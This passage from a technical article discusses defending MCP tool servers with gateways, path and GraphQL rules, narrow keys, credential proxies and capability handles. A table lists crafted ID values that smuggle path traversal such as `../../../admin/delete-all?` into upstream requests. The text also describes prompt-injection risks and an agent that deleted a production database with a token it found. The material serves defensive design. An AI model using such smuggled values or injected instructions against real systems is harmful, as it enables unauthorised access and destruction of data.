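These checks suit customer IDs because the IDs have a known format. The `query` argument of `search_tickets` has no fixed format, since an employee may need to search for any words a customer might have written. A pattern that excluded colons would block `type:user`, which returns customer accounts, but it would also block the legitimate `status:open`. Banning only `type:` would still block searches for error messages that contain it, and would miss any other operator with a similar effect.

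The gateway could parse each query and permit only certain search operators. Its parser would have to interpret quotation marks, brackets and escapes exactly as the help desk does, and the operator would have to update it whenever the help desk company added a feature.

Rewriting the search is no easier. An external program could add `type:ticket` to every query, but a caller might bypass that restriction by writing `OR` in the right place, much as a crafted cluster ID bypassed Dynatrace's filter.

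A better design divides the argument into separate fields, such as `status` with a short list of options and `text` for the words to find. The gateway can enforce the options, but the tool server still has to make sure that the search engine treats `text` as plain words, so this design requires a change to the server.

Some text is harmful without containing any special syntax. If a tool posts replies to support tickets, a message with instructions for the next agent that reads the ticket is a valid reply. Errico and colleagues point out that input validation can't protect against well-formed text that a model will interpret as a command.

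### Measuring blocked attacks and wrong refusals

In Metere's test, the gate blocked every call to an invented tool name, but the test didn't examine arguments or measure how often the gate refused legitimate work. The product documentation from Envoy AI Gateway, Traefik, agentgateway and AWS describes how to write argument rules but gives no error rates for them. One company's error rates would be of little help in predicting another's, because they depend on the format of the company's identifiers and on what its agents do.

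An operator can estimate the rate of wrong refusals by running a new rule over past calls before enforcing it. agentgateway can record the arguments in its access log, which will then contain personal data and need its own protection. If the rule refuses none of 1,000 legitimate calls, the true rate is probably below 0.3% (95% confidence), provided that future calls resemble the old ones. They might not if, for example, a merger brings in customers with new kinds of ID. Past calls may contain no attacks, so to test how well the rule stops them, the operator needs to send hostile values like those in the table through the gateway to a test copy of the tool server.

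A wrong refusal can also make later calls fail. By default, Traefik answers a forbidden call with HTTP status 403, which many clients interpret as a broken connection. Claude Desktop then can't use that server again until the user restarts the application, while VS Code recovers by itself. An operator can have Traefik return the refusal with status 200 instead, so that the client treats it as an ordinary answer. The Model Context Protocol recommends that servers report invalid input as a tool error with a useful explanation, which lets the model correct a mistake and try again. A gateway that refuses `customer 42` could reply that `id` must contain only digits.

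## What can be limited after the request is built

Even if a check on `id` fails and the operator doesn't notice, a second gateway between the tool server and the upstream API can still refuse the request, because it receives the method, host and path that the server built.

### One rule for one tool

Suppose the upstream API keeps each profile at `/api/v1/users/{id}/profile`, as in the FastMCP demonstration. `get_user_profile` then needs to send only a `GET` to that path, with one segment in place of the ID. The gateway could enforce this with a short Python function:

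```python
import re

PROFILE = re.compile(r"/api/v1/users/[A-Za-z0-9_-]+/profile")

def permitted(tool, method, host, target):
    return (
        tool == "get_user_profile"
        and method == "GET"
        and host == "api.example.com"
        and PROFILE.fullmatch(target) is not None
    )
```

`target` is the path plus any query string, exactly as the gateway will send them. `fullmatch` requires the whole text to fit the pattern, so the function refuses any request with a query string.

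Now suppose the argument check lets everything through and the tool server pastes `id` into the path without encoding it:

| `id` | Request that reaches the gateway | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `42` | `GET /api/v1/users/42/profile` | Permitted |
| `../../../admin/delete-all?` | `GET /admin/delete-all?/profile` | Refused |
| `42/invoices?` | `GET /api/v1/users/42/invoices?/profile` | Refused |
| `42/profile?include=cards&x=` | `GET /api/v1/users/42/profile?include=cards&x=/profile` | Refused |
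| `..` | `GET /api/v1/profile` | Refused |
| `43` | `GET /api/v1/users/43/profile` | Permitted |

The FastMCP attack, with `/admin/delete-all`, uses the right host and method, so only a rule that includes the path can catch it. The function rejects the request because the path isn't a profile path, however the caller got the server to build it. It doesn't search for `../` or any other sign of an attack. A request for customer 43's profile passes because its path has the same form as customer 42's.

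A rule that checks only the host would not have stopped the FastMCP attack. InfoQ's *Securing MCP in Production* recommends a list of permitted destinations because of a flaw in Microsoft's Azure MCP Server. An attacker could supply a URL where the server expected an Azure resource identifier, and the server would send its access token to that URL. Such a list can stop this kind of leak, but InfoQ's sample rule permits connections to port 443 on any internal address that begins with `10.`, about 16.8 million addresses, and doesn't examine paths.

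OpenShell, NVIDIA's sandbox software for agents, supports more detailed rules. According to NVIDIA's *Policy Schema Reference*, a rule can specify a method, a path pattern and query parameters. The pattern for profiles would be `/api/v1/users/*/profile`, but an operator should test what `*` matches. One of NVIDIA's examples uses the pattern `/repos/*/branches/*/protection` to protect branches on GitHub. GitHub's paths have two segments, the owner and the repository, between `/repos/` and `/branches/`, so the example protects those branches only if `*` can match more than one segment. In that case, the profile pattern would also accept `/api/v1/users/42/invoices/profile`.

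OpenShell's "read-only" preset is looser still. It permits `GET` on every path, including `/admin/delete-all`.

### Linking a request to its tool

The function's first condition, the tool's name, is the hardest to supply because an ordinary HTTP request doesn't contain it. According to NVIDIA, OpenShell's proxy examines the process that opened each connection, so a program can't simply claim to be another one. But a tool server usually runs all its tools in one process, so the proxy can't distinguish `get_user_profile` from `get_invoice`. NVIDIA's full example also permits `/usr/bin/node`, which covers any script that Node.js runs.

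The tool server could put the tool's name in a request header. A crafted `id` normally can't change this header because the server's code sets it separately from the path, but someone who controls that code could forge it. Matching requests to tool calls by time is unreliable because calls can overlap.

If the server lets an operator disable tools, a simpler method is to run a separate copy of the server for each sensitive tool, with all other tools turned off. The gateway can identify each copy by its network address or key, but the operator has more processes to run and update.

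Without any such link, the gateway can permit only the requests that at least one enabled tool needs. This still stops the request to `/admin/delete-all`. It also blocks requests to a disabled tool's endpoint, unless an enabled tool uses the same endpoint. But `get_user_profile` can still fetch invoices if `get_invoice` is enabled.

To write these rules, the operator has to know what each tool normally sends. *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) describes a test environment that records the requests, including parameters, that MCP servers make to outside services. An operator could draft rules from such a record and test them in OpenShell's `audit` setting, which logs violations without blocking them. To block violations, the operator has to change the setting to `enforce`.

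### Reading the request as the API does

Most APIs use HTTPS, so the gateway can't read the request's path unless it ends the encrypted connection and opens another one to the API. For this to work, the tool server must trust certificates that the gateway issues, so anyone who steals the gateway's signing key can impersonate other services to that server.

OpenShell decrypts this traffic automatically when an endpoint's entry sets the protocol to `rest`. If the entry has no protocol, the proxy passes the connection through without inspecting it, according to NVIDIA's *Customize Sandbox Policies*. An operator who forgets the protocol line therefore limits requests by host but not by path. Some APIs require a client certificate, and the operator may have to exempt those connections from decryption.

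The gateway must also parse the path the same way the upstream API does. If only the API decodes `%2F`, the gateway treats `42%2Fcards` in `/api/v1/users/42%2Fcards/profile` as a single ID, while the API treats it as two path segments. The Python function avoids this by rejecting percent signs. OpenShell rejects encoded slashes by default, but an operator can allow them for services that need them, such as the npm package registry.

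*Names Are Not Objects* (Commey, 2026) proposes, as a general rule for confining coding agents, that a checkpoint should authorise the actual object of an operation and that the operation should then use only that object. Commey's broker, a program that handles all of an agent's requests, parses each URL once, checks the parsed URL and uses it to send the request. The broker bases its decision on the scheme, host and port, but a gateway could treat the path the same way. A gateway that simplifies a path before checking it should forward the simplified path, not the original text.

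Such a check can be fast. A request that did nothing took a median of 4.0 milliseconds through Commey's broker, which ran on the same machine as the agent. A gateway elsewhere on the network would take longer.

### APIs with one URL for every operation

A path rule achieves little when the request body contains the whole command. Abdelwahab's *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that* describes how an agent deleted a production database at Railway, a company that hosts software. The agent found an API token on a user's machine and sent a `POST` to Railway's GraphQL address with the command `volumeDelete`. Railway's sample query for the user's own name and email uses the same path and method, so a gateway rule that checks only those can't block one request without blocking the other. A tool argument didn't cause this deletion, but the rule would have the same limitation if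 a tool sent the request.

The gateway therefore has to parse the body. OpenShell can restrict a GraphQL request by operation type, operation name and root fields (its outermost fields). A rule that permits only queries with the root field `me` would block `volumeDelete`. Rules based only on operation names are weak because the caller chooses the name. A caller could avoid NVIDIA's example rule against mutations named `Admin*` by using a different name.

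Root fields are also too coarse for some tools. Suppose `get_user_profile` sends this query:

```graphql
query { user(id: "42") { name plan } }
```

If the caller gets the server to add `invoices { total }` inside `user`, the root field doesn't change. To catch the addition, the gateway has to compare the whole query with a stored one, allowing only the ID to differ. This requires holding the request body in memory. OpenShell holds up to 64 KiB by default. A gateway should refuse any body too long for it to inspect.

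A log of refused requests can be misleading too. Railway's GraphQL endpoint returns HTTP status 200 for authorisation failures and puts the error in the response body, so an operator who looks only for status 403 would miss attempts that Railway blocked.

For SQL or KQL, the gateway would need a parser that agrees with the database's own. A tool with one fixed query is easier to check. The Azure server's `get_table_schema` should always send a table name followed by `| getschema`, so the gateway could require the whole query to match this pattern:

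```
[A-Za-z0-9_]+ \| getschema
```

The injected query from the Azure advisory would fail the gateway's pattern check because it contains operations the pattern doesn't allow. The gateway has to identify which tool sent each query, because the raw-query tool on the same server may legitimately send any query. For that tool, a read-only database role is a better limit than a pattern.

### Keys limited to one tool's work

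A narrower key can also reduce a tool's reach. Let F(t) be the set of requests that the gateway permits for tool t, and P(t) the set that the upstream API authorises for that tool's own key. The tool's reach is then:

R(t) = { build(a) : a ∈ A(t) } ∩ F(t) ∩ P(t)

If either F(t) or P(t) lies entirely within the declared scope S(t), the tool has no excess reach, whatever requests its code builds. The API itself enforces P(t), so a key with narrow permissions also limits requests that bypass the gateway.

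Giving each tool its own key would be a large change for many companies. According to a figure cited in *AI Identity*, 45.6% of organisations run agents on shared API keys. InfoQ recommends a separate class of credential for each tool purpose, so that a file-search tool can't control the company's cloud account. *Systematization of Knowledge* (2025), a survey of MCP security, describes ETDI, a proposal to give each tool a token that lists detailed rights, such as read-only access. The token limits upstream requests only if the upstream API, or a gateway in front of it, enforces those rights.

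Many systems also issue tokens that expire within minutes or hours. Expiry limits how long a thief can use a stolen token, but it doesn't stop a crafted argument from reaching more of the API than intended, because the token is still valid when the tool makes the call. Binding a token to a private key, which keeps a thief from using a copied token, doesn't prevent this either, because the tool server holds the key and signs whatever request its code builds.

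Narrower permissions do help, if the API offers them. GitHub lets an installed app request a token that expires after one hour and works only with chosen repositories and permissions. For a tool that reads issues (bug reports and requests) in one repository, the request could contain:

```json
{
  "repositories": ["support-docs"],
  "permissions": { "issues": "read" }
}
```

If a crafted argument made the tool try to delete a file or read another private repository, GitHub would reject the request. The program that requests these tokens needs the app's private key. Because that key can also be used to get tokens with broader access, the program should be separate from the tool server.

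A GitHub permission can allow more than a tool needs. In an older version of GitHub's permission list, write access to "contents" also covers merging branches, so a tool meant only to edit files could also merge branches.

Amazon's cloud service allows more precise limits. *Credential Broker for Agents (CB4A)* (Hartman, 2026) lists Amazon's temporary keys among the ways to issue narrow credentials. Each key can carry a session policy, and Amazon's policy language can limit that policy to one action on one object, such as reading a single stored file.

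At the other extreme, Railway's narrowest API token covers one environment, such as production, in one project. The Daily WTF's *Empty Pockets* points out that such a token can do anything within that environment, so a token made for a script that changes domain settings can also delete the database's storage. Railway also offers OAuth tokens, which an app obtains with a user's consent. They have viewer, member and admin levels, so a tool that only reads data can use a viewer token. After the deletion, Railway changed its API so that users can undo any deletion within 48 hours, which limits the damage from an overly broad token.

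Traefik's *MCP Gateway Best Practices* recommends making upstream calls with a token that carries the employee's delegated authority rather than with one powerful shared service account. If the API checks which customers the employee may see, it can then refuse a request for customer 43's profile. The employee may still have far more access than `get_user_profile` needs.

### A gateway that adds the key

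The gateway can also keep the real key and attach it only to requests that pass its rules:

1. The tool server sends its request with a placeholder instead of the key.
2. The gateway uses the placeholder to identify the tool, then checks the method, host and path.
3. If the request passes, the gateway replaces the placeholder with the real key and forwards the request.

Several products already do parts of this. Nous Research's *Egress credential-injection proxy (iron-proxy)* describes a proxy that decrypts traffic and swaps placeholder tokens for real keys. isorun's *Credential Injection* describes attaching rules on methods and paths to each credential. *Credentials & Connections*, a guide to Permit.io's outbound proxy, explains that the proxy also removes the key from responses in case the API repeats it.

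A request that bypasses the gateway then fails because it has no valid key. If a crafted `host` argument sends the request to an attacker's machine, the attacker gets only a placeholder. If each tool has its own placeholder, the gateway can also use it to select that tool's rule, but the server's code must choose the placeholder without using the caller's text.

The credential has to be added after the tool server builds the request. *Credential Injection Patterns for AI Agents* (Posta, 2026) describes a design in which agentgateway adds a user's token to a tool call before the call reaches the tool server. This keeps the token from the agent, but a server with the FastMCP flaw would still receive it and could attach it to a request for `/admin/delete-all`.

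Posta and Hartman disagree about when to use a proxy. Hartman's draft, which was due to expire in September 2026, prefers short-lived tokens wherever the API supports them, because a proxy adds a network hop and every call fails if the proxy fails. Posta, whose company sells such a gateway, would use a proxy first. A company can't convert an employee's login into that employee's GitHub, Slack or Jira token on demand. The employee has to consent in a browser, and the company then has to store the token somewhere. (GitHub's one-hour installation tokens avoid this step because they act for an app, not for a particular employee.)

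Whether a short-lived token or a proxy better limits excess reach depends on the API. A tool server with a short-lived token calls the API directly, so no proxy checks the finished request. This is fine if the API can limit the token to the tool's own operation, as Amazon's can. Railway's API tokens are broad, so only a proxy that parses GraphQL can distinguish a change to domain settings from a deletion.

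A store of keys also attracts attackers. Hartman cites LiteLLM, a gateway that holds keys for many AI providers, which was compromised in March 2026 in a campaign that affected about 500,000 corporate identities. Hartman would separate the program that approves requests from the one that holds the keys, so that breaking into one doesn't give an attacker both. How a product stores keys is also worth checking. Permit.io's gateway, for example, keeps them in plaintext unless the operator turns on its vault.

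### References that carry their own permission

With all these measures, the caller still supplies a name, and a rule or a key determines what the caller can reach with it. A capability, the alternative Hardy favoured, combines the name and the permission in one unforgeable reference.

Suppose a tool called `find_customer` looks up only the customers that the signed-in employee may see. For customer 42, it returns a long random handle, and the gateway stores this record:

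| Handle | Request it permits | Session | Expires |
|---|---|---|---|
| `prf_9fK2...` | `GET /api/v1/users/42/profile` | `8c1e` | 14:05 |

The model passes the handle to `get_user_profile`, and the tool server forwards it to the gateway. The gateway finds the record, checks the session and the time, and sends the stored request with the real key. The tool server no longer joins text to a path, so `../admin/export` is a handle with no matching record. The caller also can't reach customer 43 by changing a digit, which a path rule alone can't prevent.

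`find_customer` must check the employee's permissions before it issues a handle; otherwise the scheme adds no protection for customer 43. The tool's schema has to accept handles, and the gateway has to translate them because ordinary APIs expect a path and a key. Handles also appear in the model's conversation, where an attacker might steal them, so the record includes a session and an expiry time. *DelegateGuard* (2026) proposes agent capabilities that are also tied to a particular holder and purpose.

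Capabilities don't stop every attack through the model. If an agent has handles for customers 42 and 43, an injected instruction can still make it use the wrong one. Capabilities also suit single objects better than searches. A handle could limit `search_tickets` to one team's tickets, but the search text would need its own checks.

Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AgentCap*, built a related system for MCP. The system issues a signed token for an approved action on a resource, with an expiry time and a limited number of uses. In their banking example, permission to send money lasts 30 seconds and covers one call. The system also refuses protected arguments, such as a payment's recipient, if their values come only from untrusted content. Suresh and Gao ran two prompt injection benchmarks once each with GPT-5.4, and no attack succeeded.

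AgentCap checks its token before the call reaches the tool server, and the token doesn't cover the request that the server builds afterwards. The resource in the banking example is `bank_account/transfers`, not a particular payment. A traversal string in an argument that the policy doesn't protect could still change the upstream path.

### Comparing the measures

| Measure | What it stops | What it misses | What it costs to run |
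|---|---|---|---|
| List of permitted hosts | Requests that send keys or data to an attacker's machine | Wrong endpoints on the right host | Updates when a tool needs a new service |
| Rule on method and path | The FastMCP attack and other wrong endpoints | The wrong customer's profile, and operations that share one URL | A rule for each tool, decryption and a short delay |
| Rule on GraphQL root fields | Commands such as `volumeDelete` | Extra fields inside a permitted one | A parser and memory for request bodies |
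| Narrow key for each tool | Anything the key can't do, even if the request bypasses the gateway | Operations that the API groups under the same permission | More keys to issue, replace and revoke |
| Short-lived token | Use of a stolen token after it expires | Misuse during the call | A service that issues tokens |
| Key added after the check | Theft of the key from the tool server, and requests that bypass the gateway | Harmful requests that the rules permit | A store of keys to protect, and an outage if the gateway fails |
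| Capability for one object | Requests for anything the caller has no handle for | Misuse of a handle that the caller does have | Changes to the tools, and a gateway or API that accepts handles |

An operator can often add a list of hosts, a path rule and a narrower key without changing the tool server's code, so these are sensible first steps with someone else's server. They are less effective for an API such as Railway's, which has one URL and broad API tokens. If an agent needs only a few operations from such an API, replacing the tool with one that sends fixed GraphQL queries may be less work than maintaining a gateway that parses them.
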